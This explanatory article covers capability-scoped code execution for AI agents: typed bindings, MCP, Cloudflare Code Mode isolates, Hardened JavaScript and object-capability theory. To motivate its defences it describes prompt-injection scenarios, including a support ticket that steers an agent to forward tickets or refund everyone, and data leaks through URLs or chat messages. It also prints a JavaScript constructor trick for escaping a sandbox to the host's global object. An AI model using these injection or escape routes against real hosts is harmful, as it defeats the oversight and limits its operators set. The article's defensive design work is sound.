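# Capability-scoped code execution: agent programs that can only call typed bindings

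## What is capability-scoped code execution?

Capability-scoped code execution is a way for an AI agent to act by writing short programs that can only call a few functions provided by a trusted program, the host. Each function does one specific job, such as looking up a customer. The agent's program cannot open a file, reach the internet or read a password on its own. The name comes from computer security, where a capability is an unforgeable reference that identifies a resource and grants the right to use it.

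Here, an AI agent is a large language model working in a loop. It reads a task, requests an action, reads the result and requests the next action, until it has finished. Many agents make these requests one at a time, and software checks each request before carrying it out. An agent that writes programs can make hundreds of requests with a few lines of code. This can save a lot of time and money, but it also makes it less clear how much checking each request helps.

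### Tool calls and schemas

A language model produces only text, so another program has to run the function that looks up the weather or refunds a customer. *Code Mode*, a September 2025 post by Varda and Pai for the infrastructure company Cloudflare, explains how the model requests this by writing text. In training, the model learns to mark the start and end of a request with special markers. Between them it writes a short message in JSON, a common text format for structured data, with the function's name and arguments. When the closing marker appears, the software around the model pauses it and parses the message. The agent program then runs the function, and the result is added to the model's input before the model continues writing. Such a request is called a tool call. Because the model never executes anything, the software that receives a request can always refuse it.

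That software checks each call against a schema, a machine-readable statement of the names, types, ranges and allowed values of the call's arguments. If the schema for a refund tool requires a whole number from 1 to 50, the software rejects a request for 51, 12.5 or "everything". Schemas can express little beyond such constraints. Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* (2025) gives the example of a tool that files support tickets. Its schema can require that the due date be text and that the priority be one of four words, but it doesn't specify which date format the system expects or how the escalation level should relate to the priority. Anthropic was discussing malformed calls rather than malicious ones, but the same gap matters for security, because a schema that limits the size of a refund can't check whether the customer deserves one.

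Many tools now share one format for all this, the Model Context Protocol (MCP). Anthropic launched this open standard in November 2024 to connect AI applications to outside systems such as databases and search engines. An agent asks an MCP server for a list of its tools, which includes each tool's name, description and input schema, and then calls a tool by name. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that governs this exchange, requires servers to validate all inputs, control access and limit the rate of calls. It also recommends, but does not require, that a human always be able to deny a call.

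An agent can make a well-formed request that nobody wanted. The main worry is prompt injection, in which the model follows text in the data it reads as if it were an instruction. For example, a customer might write in a support ticket that the agent should forward the last ten tickets to an outside address. Varda and Pai point out that a model reads a tool's result the same way it reads its user's words, apart from the special markers around the result. The markers show where the text came from, but nothing in the mechanism forces the model to treat that text only as data.

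A stranger may therefore have influenced any code that a model writes after reading such a ticket. Developers run this code in a sandbox, an environment that limits what the code can reach. *From Question Answering to Task Completion* (2026), a survey of agent design, lists the usual limits on file access, network traffic out of the sandbox (egress), running other processes, and the use of resources such as memory. Approval policies add to these limits by making certain actions wait for a human.

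### Three interfaces

A developer can let the model act through single tool calls, a general shell, or a program that can call only typed functions.

Single tool calls are the easiest to oversee. *DADL* (2026), which proposes a language for companies to describe their tools to agents, attributes this to the fixed schema of every request, which lets a client, a gateway or an audit system inspect and approve the request without running anything. The drawback is that the model has to write out each request and read each result.

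A shell, the text interface for giving commands to an operating system, is at the other extreme. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (2026) describes a typical arrangement in which an Ubuntu Linux system runs inside a container (a walled-off environment on a shared machine), with a Python interpreter and a tool that runs any command in the bash shell. The paper calls bash a "meta-tool" because the model can use it to install packages, run programs and create further tools. Running a command this way is still a tool call with a schema, but the schema need only require one piece of text, the command, and almost any action can be written as a command. Protection therefore has to come from the container, and any command the model writes may be able to use whatever the developer left inside it, including a network connection or a stored password.

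Between the two lies a program that can compute freely but can act on the outside world only through bindings. A binding is a live object or function that the host places in the program's scope and that performs an action the host has already authorised. The Model Context Protocol project sets out the steps in its guidance for developers:

1. The host reads the schemas of the available tools and generates a typed function for each.
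2. The model writes a script that uses those functions.
3. The sandbox runs the script. When the script reaches one of the functions, the function passes its name and arguments out to the host and waits.
4. The host checks the call against what the user has allowed, adds the access token that the outside service needs, makes the call and returns the result to the script.
5. The model receives only what the script prints or returns at the end.

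The script never holds the access token, and the sandbox needs no network connection, because the host carries out every action outside the sandbox. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* follows this pattern closely. Each program runs in a fresh instance of V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. It has no direct network access or general-purpose filesystem, and it cannot install packages or start other processes. It can affect outside systems only through tools the developer enabled for that request. Vaughan (2026), in *Programmatic Tool Calling*, links the feature to the general release of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 on 9 July 2026. Cloudflare's Code Mode, from September 2025, also builds on V8.

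Some systems give the model a similar interface but rely on a different security argument. *MM-ToolSandBox* (2026), a benchmark for agents that handle images, lets models use either structured tool calls or free-form Python in which the tools appear as ordinary functions, an approach it traces to work from 2024. Its interpreter rejects disallowed imports and unsafe operations before execution, restricts file access and dangerous system calls at run time, and caps memory, running time and output. This design appears to start with normal Python and remove dangerous powers, so the guardrails have to block each one the code might use. A capability-scoped program starts with no powers and gains only those the host adds, so if the host forgets one, the program can do too little, which is usually the safer mistake.

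### Why developers moved to code

The case for code was mostly about efficiency. Anthropic's November 2025 post *Code execution with MCP* described two problems for agents with access to hundreds or thousands of tools. The tool definitions filled the model's context window, the limited amount of text it can take in at once, before the model had read the user's request. Every intermediate result also had to pass through the model on its way to the next call.

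Anthropic's example of the second problem is a request to download a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attach it to a sales record in Salesforce. With single tool calls, the download puts the transcript into the model's context, and the model then has to write it all out again as an argument of the update. This is slow, and the model may make copying errors if the document is long. In the code version, which Willison (2025) reprinted on his weblog in *Code execution with MCP*, the script stores the transcript in a variable and passes the variable to the update function, so the transcript never enters the model's context. Willison, an independent commentator on these tools, found the idea sound but noted that Anthropic had published no working implementation.

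A script can filter data in the same way, fetching a spreadsheet of 10,000 rows and printing only the five that matter. Loops help when an agent would otherwise have to alternate between checking and waiting. In another of Anthropic's examples, the agent needs to know when a deployment notice appears in a chat channel, and a short loop can watch for it without calling the model between checks.

A later example from Anthropic combines these. A manager asks which members of a team exceeded their travel budget for the quarter. The agent has one tool that lists the team, one that returns a person's expenses and one that returns the budget for each level of seniority. If the model calls the tools one at a time for a team of twenty, it makes twenty expense requests, each returning 50 to 100 items, and has to add up more than 2,000 items by reading them. A program instead fetches the expenses in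 parallel, adds them up in code and prints the names of the two or three people who went over. In Anthropic's illustration of November 2025, usage falls from 150,000 tokens (the word fragments in which models read and write) to 2,000. The measurements in Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* are more modest. Billed input tokens fell by roughly 38 percent on a benchmark with 75 tools, while cost rose by roughly 8 percent on one where each turn needs only a call or two.

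Keeping data out of the model's context also affects safety, for better and worse. Anthropic presented it as a privacy gain, because customers' phone numbers can move from a spreadsheet to a sales system without the model seeing them. It plausibly helps against prompt injection too, since the model cannot follow instructions it never reads. But a model that never sees the intermediate results cannot notice when they look wrong, so the program continues with the logic the model wrote before any data arrived.

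Anthropic cautions that running agent-written code requires a secure environment with sandboxing, resource limits and monitoring, which add operational overhead and security considerations that direct tool calls avoid. Its proposal also assumed a less restricted setting than the one OpenAI later built, in which the agent browses tool definitions stored as files and its scripts can save their work to disk. OpenAI is more specific about when to use code. It recommends programs for stages with predictable control flow, and direct tool calls by default for writes and for actions that need approval, "to preserve a clear authorization boundary".

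### A support agent

Consider a company that uses an agent to handle customer complaints. The host gives the agent four bindings:

```
tickets.list()
customers.get(id)
refunds.issue(orderId, amount)    // amount: an integer from 1 to 50
mail.send(to, body)
```

The agent can read the open tickets, look up a customer, refund all or part of an order in whole dollars up to $50, and send an email. It has no other way to affect anything. Under OpenAI's advice, refunds and emails should probably stay outside programs, because refunds move money and sent emails can't be recalled. Developers will still want to automate both because they make up most of a support desk's work, which makes the example a fair test.

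Through single tool calls, a refund of 20 dollars on one order is a request like this:

```json
{
  "name": "refunds.issue",
  "arguments": { "orderId": "A-1042", "amount": 20 }
}
```

The host checks the arguments against the schema, confirms that they are a piece of text and a whole number between 1 and 50, and issues the refund. The model reads the confirmation and decides what to do next. If the company wants a person to approve refunds, that person sees one order number and one amount.

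Now suppose a courier has had a bad week, and the company tells the agent to give 10 dollars to everyone who complained of a late delivery. With the same four bindings the model can write:

```javascript
const open = await tickets.list();
const late = open.filter(t => t.topic === "late delivery");
let total = 0;
for (const t of late) {
  const customer = await customers.get(t.customerId);
  await refunds.issue(t.orderId, 10);
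  await mail.send(customer.email, "We have refunded $10 for the delay.");
  total += 10;
}
console.log(`${late.length} refunds, $${total} in total`);
```

`await` makes the program wait for the host's response. If thirty tickets concern late deliveries, the program makes 91 calls: one to list the tickets, then a lookup, a refund and an email for each of the thirty. The program's trace is the ordered list of those calls with their arguments, but the model reads only one line at the end.

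Every refund in that trace satisfies the schema. If the program had computed an amount of 75, a host that checks arguments would have refused the call, just as it refuses a direct one. But the filter in the second line determines who gets money, and no schema covers it. If a sentence hidden in one of the tickets had led the model to leave out the filter, the program would have refunded every open ticket, and each refund would still have satisfied the schema.

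The schema never prevented this, since a model that makes single tool calls can also refund the wrong thirty people, one after another. But single calls allow a pause after each result, in which the model might reconsider or a person might step in, and each request is simple enough to judge at a glance. Programs weaken both safeguards. As *DADL* notes, the host can still inspect a script before running it, but this requires analysing code rather than matching a request against a schema, and an injected prompt may add code that builds unexpected calls. The Model Context Protocol guidance says that approving a script must not count as approving every call it makes, and that the host has to evaluate each call as it arrives. The limit of 50 dollars therefore still applies to every refund, but checking each call doesn't tell the host whether there should be thirty of them. A loop that issued a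 thousand refunds would pass the same check a thousand times.

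## What does it mean for a program to hold no ambient authority?

A limit of 50 dollars per refund protects the company only if the agent's program has no other way to reach the payment system. On an ordinary computer, it might well have one. A script started from a shell can usually open every file its user can open and connect to any server, even though nobody gave it those files or connections. This is ambient authority, the power that code has merely by running in a particular process or under a particular account.

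*Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) defines ambient authority as authority that a program exercises without selecting it. The paper compares this to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens when the right person walks up. In Unix, for example, a program requests a file by giving the operating system only the file's name, and the system allows or refuses the request based on the account the program runs under. The program cannot specify which of its rights to use, and an attacker can exploit that.

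### The confused deputy

The standard example comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988). Hardy calls the story "nearly true" and sets it in about 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. It involves a compiler, which translates source code into a form the machine can run.

1. The compiler was in a directory called SYSX. Users ran it by name and could also name a file to receive debugging output.
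2. Tymshare's engineers wanted statistics on which language features people used, so they made the compiler record them in a file called STAT, also in SYSX. To permit this, they gave the compiler a licence to write to files in its own directory.
3. SYSX also contained BILL, the file that held the billing information.
4. A user learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output.
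5. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which found that the compiler had a licence for SYSX and opened the file. The debugging output overwrote the billing information.

The compiler had the right to write to BILL, and the user only had to supply the name.

Hardy explains why the obvious repairs were inadequate. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but that directory didn't exist when the programmers wrote the code, and some users might have legitimate access to files in it. It could refuse BILL in particular, but SYSX held other sensitive files, and someone would have to change the compiler whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare did add a system call that let a program choose between its own authority and its user's, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities.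 The rules for opening a file also kept growing, and the last time Hardy wrote them down, they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors".

He thought the problem was that the compiler acted for two parties and couldn't keep their authority separate. With capabilities, the compiler holds a reference to STAT from the start, and the user passes it a reference to the output file instead of a name. The compiler writes statistics to STAT and debugging output to the user's file. A user without a capability for BILL can't pass one, even if they know the file's name. The compiler needs no extra check, because the reference that identifies the file also carries the permission to write to it.

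Miller and colleagues caution that removing ambient authority makes such mistakes avoidable but doesn't rule them out. A program that holds several capabilities and tries each one until a request succeeds can still use the wrong party's capability.

The support agent's bindings repeat part of Tymshare's design. `mail.send(to, body)` takes the address as text and sends the mail with the host's authority. If a stranger's ticket has influenced the program, the stranger may have chosen the address. A schema can confirm that the address is well formed, but (SYSX)BILL was also a well-formed file name. So a program with no ambient authority can still turn its host into a confused deputy if the bindings accept names where they could accept references.

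### How a program can get a reference

The idea of capabilities is older than Hardy's story. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) traces it to a 1966 paper by Dennis and Van Horn. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, a doctoral thesis, sets out the rules in a form that fits both operating systems and programming languages. In his model, objects can affect one another only by sending messages along references, and an object can come to hold a reference in four ways:

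- It already held the reference when the system started.
- It created the object that the reference points to.
- Its creator held the reference and built it in.
- Another object, which held references to both, passed it along in a message.

The support agent's program gets its four bindings in the third way, from the host that creates it. It can create functions and lists, but it can receive further references only if a binding returns them. If no chain of references leads from the program to the payroll database, no code the language model writes can reach it. Miller summarizes this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". The capability model is therefore well suited to code that nobody has reviewed, because the guarantee depends on what the host handed over and not on what the code does.

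The rules don't protect plain data. Miller notes that a program can have any number it can work out, whether that number is 7 or someone's private key. Passwords and access tokens are plain data, so a program that has seen one can copy it anywhere it can send text.

A component that Miller calls a loader turns the model's text into a running program. It takes the code and a table that maps each outside name in the code to what it refers to. In a properly isolated loader, that table is the program's only source of references. If the loader also resolves names that aren't in the table but give the program power, Miller calls them magic names, and the host can't withhold them. Python's built-in `open`, which opens files, is a magic name in most Python environments.

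### Permission and authority

These rules determine which functions a program can call directly, which Miller calls its permissions, but not everything it can bring about, which he calls its authority. In his example, Bob doesn't have permission to write to a Unix system's password file. Alice does, and she writes whatever text Bob asks her to, so Bob has the authority to write to the file through her.

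The support program has permission to call four functions, but its authority is wider because those calls let it spend the company's money, 50 dollars at a time, and email any text to anyone. If a colleague or another agent acts on one of those emails, the effects of that action may also be within the program's authority.

A list of permissions is therefore an unsafe basis for a security review. Calculating the exact authority isn't feasible either, because it depends on how every program involved will behave. Miller's answer is to calculate something larger that is easier to find:

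EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA

EA is the authority a program will eventually have. TA is the authority it could have if every object did anything its references allow. TA is easy to find by following references, but it is so large that a reviewer who relied on it would reject many safe designs. To find BA, the reviewer reads the code of a few trusted objects to see what they actually do, and assumes the other objects could do anything their references allow. Any action outside BA is also outside EA, so the reviewer can safely rule it out.

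For an agent, the bindings are trusted and the programs the model writes are not. A reviewer can read the four short binding functions once and treat every future program as hostile. In this analysis, a schema limits only permission, while authority also depends on what the host does with each call and how the program combines calls.

### Weaker and revocable bindings

A host can narrow a program's authority by wrapping a capability in a weaker one, which is called attenuation. Instead of handing over `mail.send`, the host can keep it and make a function that answers one ticket:

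```javascript
// runs in the host
function makeReply(ticket) {
  const sender = ticket.from;
  return body => mail.send(sender, body);
}
```

The host calls `makeReply` for each open ticket and attaches the result to the ticket as `reply`. The loop that compensates customers for late deliveries then no longer needs `customers.get` or an address:

```javascript
for (const t of late) {
  await refunds.issue(t.orderId, 10);
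  await t.reply("We have refunded $10 for the delay.");
}
```

The program can call `reply`, but it can't read or change the variable `sender` inside it. If `reply` looked up `ticket.from` at every call instead of using the address copied into `sender`, a program that could alter the ticket could redirect the reply.

A hidden instruction to forward tickets to an outside address now fails, because the program has no function that accepts an address. But a program that holds ten tickets and ten reply functions can still paste the text of nine tickets into its reply to the tenth, whose sender may be the attacker. Running a separate program for each ticket would prevent this, but it would also give up the batch processing that made code attractive. How narrowly to grant bindings for each task therefore depends partly on how much efficiency the designer is willing to lose.

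Wrappers can also keep information between calls. A version of `refunds.issue` that tracks its total payout and stops at 500 dollars would end a loop of 10-dollar refunds after fifty.

Revocation uses a similar wrapper. Miller credits the pattern, known as the caretaker, to work by Redell in 1974. His version is in the language E. In JavaScript it could look like this:

```javascript
function makeRevocable(target) {
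  let enabled = true;
  const forwarder = (...args) => {
    if (!enabled) throw new Error("revoked");
    return target(...args);
  };
  const revoke = () => { enabled = false; };
  return { forwarder, revoke };
}
```

The host gives the program `forwarder` and keeps `revoke`. While `enabled` is true, the forwarder passes each call to the real function. After the host calls `revoke`, the program still holds the forwarder, but calling it produces an error. Anyone the program shared the forwarder with gets the same error, since the program never had the real function to share.

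A caretaker is only safe if the function behind it doesn't return other useful references. If the host wraps `tickets.list` in a caretaker and later revokes it, any ticket the program has already fetched still has a working `reply`. Miller's solution is a membrane, which wraps every capability that passes through it in either direction and lets the host disable all of them together. Data passes through unwrapped, because the host can't take back data the program has already read, such as ticket text.

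Wrappers like these are short but can contain subtle errors. *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns* (Swasey, Garg and Dreyer, 2017) presents a formal logic for proving that such patterns protect an object's private state from unknown code, with results verified in the proof assistant Coq.

### Can capabilities be confined and revoked?

For decades, researchers argued that capability systems had basic defects in confinement and revocation. Confinement means running an untrusted program without letting it leak data or pass on its access. Karger wrote in 1988 of "a fundamental inability to solve the confinement problem". Wallach and others argued in 1997 that two programs able to exchange references can share their capabilities without the system intervening, so every program that holds a capability has to be trustworthy. Chander, Dean and Mitchell called revocation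 infeasible in 2001, arguing that nobody can take a reference away from its holder.

Miller and colleagues reply that both objections treat capabilities as keys, which people can copy and hand to anyone. In an object-capability system, a program can pass a reference only to an object it can already reach. The host keeps one program from sharing its access with another by making sure that no chain of references connects them. They concede that the holder keeps its reference after revocation, but the host revokes the access behind it, using a forwarder like the one above.

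Miller and colleagues also answer Boebert's influential 1984 argument. Boebert imagined a low-security program and a high-security program under a rule that information may flow up but never down. The high program can read the low program's memory but can't write to it. In his attack, the low program stores its own capability to write to that memory in the memory itself. The high program reads the capability and can then use it to write secrets where the low program can read them. Miller and colleagues accept that the attack works if a capability is a string of bits that can travel wherever data can. But most capability systems keep references and data apart, so the right to read data doesn't include the right to fetch capabilities.

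The reply is convincing for systems that make this separation, but a good deal of ordinary software doesn't. Many web services accept an access token, which is a string of bits, from anyone who presents it. If the host gave the support program its token for the payment service, the program could email the token to a stranger, who could then issue refunds with no 50-dollar limit. Keeping the token in the host avoids this.

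Miller's argument about confinement leaves out covert channels, such as signalling through the timing of events. It also applies only to a program that starts in an environment its user controls, because a service already running elsewhere might hold references nobody knows about. An agent's program meets that condition because the host creates it afresh, but the outside services behind its bindings don't. Once the host grants a binding that sends email, the program can use it to pass data out without a covert channel.

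### What a language has to remove

Miller's rules hold only if the language provides no other way to obtain a reference, and most popular languages provide several. In C++, a program can convert a number into a pointer and so forge a reference. In Java, two objects can communicate through a global variable that any code may change, even if neither was given a reference to the other. Reflection, which lets a program examine and alter other objects as it runs, breaks the rules if it exposes private state. Imports break them if a program can get a powerful library just by naming it. Java lets a host decide what most imported names mean, but Miller found that the host couldn't override certain system classes, including some powerful ones.

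Language designers have either created a new language or restricted an existing one. Miller's thesis presents E, a new language built on the capability rules. Even E's loader recognises a few names that nobody supplied, such as `true` and `throw`, which Miller calls "mostly harmless" because none of them provides authority. *Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) instead defines a subset of Java intended to let reviewers check a program's security properties. Global variables remain, but they must be constants that hold only unchangeable data. Mettler points out that every Joe-E program is also a valid Java program, so programmers can keep their existing tools. Scala's tracked capabilities go further by recording in a value's type which capabilities the value can use.

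Google's Caja project took the restrictive approach to JavaScript so that websites could include code from strangers. The documentation of *SES*, a JavaScript library, describes it as starting where Caja left off. SES implements Hardened JavaScript, a proposed mode of the language. Its listed users include Agoric, which uses it to confine smart contracts, and MetaMask, which uses it to confine plugins.

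### Hardened JavaScript step by step

JavaScript needs such a mode because code running side by side normally shares the language's built-in objects. All arrays, for instance, get their `filter` method from one object. If the agent's program shared these built-ins with the host, it could replace `filter` with its own function. The next time the host filtered a list of customers, it would run the program's function and give it the whole list.

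The host prevents this by calling `lockdown()`, which freezes the shared built-ins so that no program can replace their methods. It then creates a compartment, an environment with its own global object, and puts the bindings there:

```javascript
import 'ses';
lockdown();

const sandbox = new Compartment({
  globals: harden({ tickets, refunds, print }),
  __options__: true,
});
sandbox.evaluate(source);   // the program the model wrote
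```

The `__options__` line is a temporary requirement of the library. Inside the compartment, the program can use frozen built-ins such as `Array` and the three objects the host supplied, and it reports its result with `print`. It has no `fetch` for making network requests. Lockdown also disables the clock and the random number generator for code in the compartment. Two programs that share a generator can signal to each other through the numbers they use up, and a precise clock can help a program infer what other code is doing.

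`harden` freezes an object and everything reachable through its properties, so no program can swap `refunds.issue` for something else. It doesn't freeze variables hidden inside functions, so a refund wrapper can still update its running total and a caretaker can switch off. The host must be careful about what it shares, because a hardened `Map`, JavaScript's built-in lookup table, remains writable by anyone who holds it.

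Freezing alone would leave a less obvious route open. Every JavaScript function has a link to a constructor that can build new functions from text. In ordinary JavaScript, a program that received `refunds.issue` from the host could write:

```javascript
refunds.issue.constructor("return globalThis")()
```

The constructor belongs to the host's environment, so the new function would run there and return the host's global object and everything in it. One harmless-looking binding would give the program the host's ambient authority. Lockdown replaces this constructor with one that only throws an error. The program can still build functions with its own `Function`, but they run inside the compartment.

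Finding every such route is difficult. According to the *SES* documentation, three engineers spent four weeks assessing the library in June 2021 and found no previously unknown vulnerabilities, and a joint bug hunt with MetaMask the next month found no critical flaws. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Ses package* lists two later holes in confinement. In 2023, JavaScript's dynamic `import` and spread operator could let a confined program leak information or run arbitrary code. In 2025, variables that a web page had declared at the top level of a script became visible inside compartments. Both holes involved everyday features of the language, and more seem likely. A designer who starts with a large language has to close every route to a reference, so even a capability system keeps some of the risk of removing powers one by one.

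Compartments also don't limit a program's resource use. A confined program can run forever or allocate any amount of memory, and an infinite loop in one compartment halts every other program in the same environment, including the host's code. The project therefore recommends combining compartments with separate processes or workers.

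## How does a V8 isolate confine agent code to its bindings?

Hardened JavaScript has to freeze the language's built-in objects because the host and the confined program share them. Cloudflare's Code Mode avoids the sharing by running each program in a new isolate, a separate instance of the V8 engine with its own heap and built-ins. A program that replaces the `filter` method changes it only for itself. The `refunds.issue.constructor` trick also fails, because that constructor belongs to the program's own isolate, not to the host.

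An isolate also starts with no way to open a file or a network connection, because JavaScript has no built-in functions for either. The software that embeds the engine has to add them. According to Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works*, a Code Mode program gets JavaScript's standard globals, but no host credentials, no unrestricted network access and none of the functions of Node.js, the environment that usually runs JavaScript on servers. The program needs bindings to reach anything outside the isolate.

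### One run from start to finish

Suppose the support company offers its four tools through an MCP server. A run broadly follows the steps in the Model Context Protocol guidance, and Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers*, the documentation for the sandbox, and Varda and Pai fill in the details:

1. The host fetches the tools' schemas and translates them into TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with type annotations. Each tool becomes a function, and its description becomes a comment.
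2. The host offers the model a single tool, which takes one piece of text called `code`. The tool's description contains the generated TypeScript.
3. The model writes a function that does the work. The host tidies it, for example by removing formatting marks around the code and wrapping loose statements in a function.
4. The host loads the code into a fresh isolate, along with an object called `codemode`.
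5. The program calls `codemode.refunds_issue(...)`. The `codemode` object contains no refund code. It forwards the function's name and arguments to the host by remote procedure call (RPC), a way to call a function that runs elsewhere, and the program waits.
6. The host makes the call to the MCP server with its own access token and passes the result back.
7. When the program ends, the host gives the model its return value and everything it printed with `console.log`. It then discards the isolate.

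For refunds, the generated TypeScript might look like this:

```typescript
declare const codemode: {
  /** Refund all or part of an order. */
  refunds_issue: (input: {
    orderId: string;
    amount: number;
  }) => Promise<{ [key: string]: any }>;
  // ...and the other three tools
};
```

`Promise` marks a result that the program has to `await`. TypeScript's `number` type has no upper limit, so the 50-dollar cap has to be enforced outside the program.

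Varda and Pai report that agents can handle more tools, and more complex ones, in this form than as separate tool calls. They attribute this to training data, which includes code from millions of open-source projects but only a contrived set of tool calls. Their post gives no measurements for this claim.

The first version put the whole interface into the model's context, which becomes a problem again with hundreds of tools. The current version gives the model only the names of the connected services. The model can first write a program that calls `codemode.search()` to find relevant functions and `codemode.describe()` to get their types, then write its real program for a second run. This saves tokens but doesn't restrict the program, which can call any function of a connected service whether or not the model looked it up.

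### What the host puts into the isolate

Cloudflare calls a program on its platform a Worker. A Dynamic Worker is one that another Worker creates while it runs, using a component called the Worker Loader. For a support agent that may read tickets and issue refunds, but not send mail, the host could write:

```javascript
const worker = env.LOADER.load({
  compatibilityDate: "2026-03-01",
  mainModule: "agent.js",
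  modules: { "agent.js": agentCode },
  env: { TICKETS: tickets, REFUNDS: refunds },
  globalOutbound: null,
});
await worker.getEntrypoint().run();
```

- `compatibilityDate` selects the version of the platform's behaviour that the program gets, so that later changes to the platform don't break it.
- `modules` holds the source code as a table of file names and their contents, and `mainModule` names the file to start with. `agentCode` is the text the model wrote. The loader doesn't translate TypeScript, so the model has to write plain JavaScript or the host has to convert the code first.
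- `env` holds the bindings. The program can use `env.TICKETS` and `env.REFUNDS`, but there is no `env.MAIL`, because the host didn't supply one.
- `globalOutbound: null` makes the functions for network access throw an error. A host that omits this line usually gives the program full internet access.

The last line of the example starts the program by calling a function named `run` in the model's code.

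The Worker Loader closely resembles Miller's loader, with `env` as its table of outside names. But every Worker also has the network functions `fetch` and `connect`, even if they aren't in `env`. These are magic names in Miller's sense, though the host can disable them, unlike Python's `open`.

`env` can also hold ordinary data such as numbers and text. This is convenient for passing settings, but the program can read any API key that a developer puts there as text.

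A host can create an isolate with `load` or `get`. `load` makes a new one every time, which Cloudflare recommends for one-off agent code. `get` takes an ID and may reuse an isolate that is still in memory. Cloudflare warns that the same ID must always stand for exactly the same content, including `env`. If a host used the ID `support-agent` for two customers with different bindings, the second customer's request could run in an isolate that holds the first customer's bindings. The ID would then select the wrong customer's authority, much as a file name selected the compiler's authority at Tymshare.

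### How a reference crosses the boundary

The program and the host have separate memories, so the program can't hold an ordinary reference to a host object. Instead, it holds a stub, a local object that forwards each method call to the original. Stubs follow Miller's rules between isolates. Cloudflare's *Bindings* explains that they have no global identifier, and that a program can't forge a stub and can only obtain one by receiving it.

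Stubs also allow attenuation. The earlier `makeReply` function, which could answer only one ticket's sender, would look like this as a binding:

```javascript
// runs in the host
export class TicketReply extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async send(body) {
    const { apiKey, address } = this.ctx.props;
    await sendMail(apiKey, address, body);
  }
}

const reply = ctx.exports.TicketReply({
  props: { apiKey: MAIL_KEY, address: ticket.from },
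});
```

If the host puts `reply` into `env` as `REPLY`, the program can call `env.REPLY.send("We have refunded $10.")`. The host sets `props` when it creates the stub, and only the method in the host can read them, so the program cannot access the key or the address. One class can serve every ticket because each stub has its own `props`.

The same technique can divide a shared database among customers. In another of Cloudflare's examples, the host's method adds the customer's prefix to every key the program asks for. A request for `settings` returns the entry `customer-42:settings`, and the program cannot name another customer's entry.

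The program and the host can each pass references to the other. *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* gives the example of a chat room where the program passes its own function to `subscribe`, and the host calls that function whenever a message arrives. A binding can also return a new stub, which gives the program whatever powers that stub carries. Reviewers should therefore check what a binding returns as carefully as what it accepts.

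### A binding compared with a key

Cloudflare describes a binding as "a permission and an API in one piece". Varda and Pai contrast this with the usual arrangement, in which a program has general network access and sends an API key, a secret that identifies the caller, with each request. If the support program worked this way, it could request a $5,000 refund from the payment service, do anything else the key allows, or send the key to a stranger.

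A safer arrangement keeps the key in the host and routes the program's web requests through a gateway, which adds the key before forwarding them. Cloudflare supports this too, and it hides the key as well as bindings do.

The stronger argument for bindings is that they set clearer limits. Varda and colleagues point out that a gateway must fully interpret a request before deciding whether to allow it, and web requests have many headers and parameters that might matter. To enforce the 50-dollar limit, the gateway would have to recognise every kind of request that moves money, including any the payment service adds later. A refund binding takes only an order number and an amount from the program and builds the request itself. Varda and Pai add that clear limits also help the model, since it doesn't have to predict which requests the gateway will block.

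This argument is convincing when a developer has written the binding with a particular limit in mind. But Code Mode can also generate bindings from existing tools, and these bindings allow everything the tools allow. The interface in Varda and Pai's example includes a function that fetches the content of any web address. A program could send a customer's details to a stranger's server by putting them in the address.

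Code Mode can also generate bindings from an OpenAPI document, a common machine-readable description of a web service. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode API reference*, these bindings always include a general `request` function. To limit what the program does with `request`, the host must go back to checking arbitrary requests, as a gateway does.

### What hiding the key prevents

Varda and Pai claim that, with bindings, the AI "cannot possibly write code that leaks any keys". For keys that stay in the host, this seems right as long as the code can't escape the isolate, because the program never receives them. The claim doesn't cover every secret, though. If a customer has pasted a password into a support ticket, `tickets.list` will return it.

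Developers can also expose keys by accident. In Cloudflare's system for long-running workflows, the host attaches metadata to each workflow. The program can read this metadata, so Cloudflare tells developers not to put keys or tokens in it.

A more serious limitation is that a program can use the access a key grants without seeing the key. In Cloudflare's example, an agent uses a binding to post to one chat room, and the host adds the key, the room and the bot's name to every message. Cloudflare writes that the agent has no way to "see or use the API key", but although the agent can't see the key, every message it posts uses it. The agent can post any text it likes, including passages from private documents it has read through other bindings. It might even be able to appear under another name. The host puts `[Robo]:` at the start of each message, but if the chat service displays line breaks,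 the program could add a second line that starts with `[Alice]:`.

Hiding the key greatly limits the damage an attacker can do. A stolen payment key keeps working until the company notices and replaces it. An attacker who controls only the program has to go through the host's refund function while the program is running, and the host can log every call. But the program could still refund thirty wrong customers in one short run. Some effects also outlast the run. If a binding let the program create a mail-forwarding rule, the rule would keep sending mail out after the host had discarded the isolate.

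### From closed beta to paid service

When Varda and Pai introduced Code Mode in September 2025, developers could try the Worker Loader on their own machines but had to join a closed beta to use it in production. In February 2026, Cloudflare released a rewritten Code Mode library. It produces a tool that developers can give to a model of their choice, whereas the old library called the language model itself. The new library can also run the code in other companies' sandboxes.

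The rewrite also changed how the program gets its bindings. According to the release notes in NewReleases' *github cloudflare/agents @cloudflare/codemode@0.1.0*, the host now passes the object that forwards tool calls as an argument when it starts the program, instead of putting it in `env`. In Miller's model, the program now gets this reference in a message rather than at its creation, but the host still decides what to hand over.

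The sandbox became available to all paying Workers customers on 24 March 2026, with Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers, now in open beta* (2026). Two days later, Cloudflare's *Code mode for MCP server portals* (2026) announced that Code Mode was on by default in its portals, which give agents access to several MCP servers through one address. Cloudflare waived the charge for creating Dynamic Workers until 26 May. Beyond a monthly allowance of 1,000, each one now costs $0.002 per day, and every one-off agent program counts separately. The documentation from October 2026 still restricts the service to the paid plan. In August, InfoQ's *Cloudflare OS* (2026) reported that Cloudflare had also released an open-source AI platform for businesses, built on a capability-based model.

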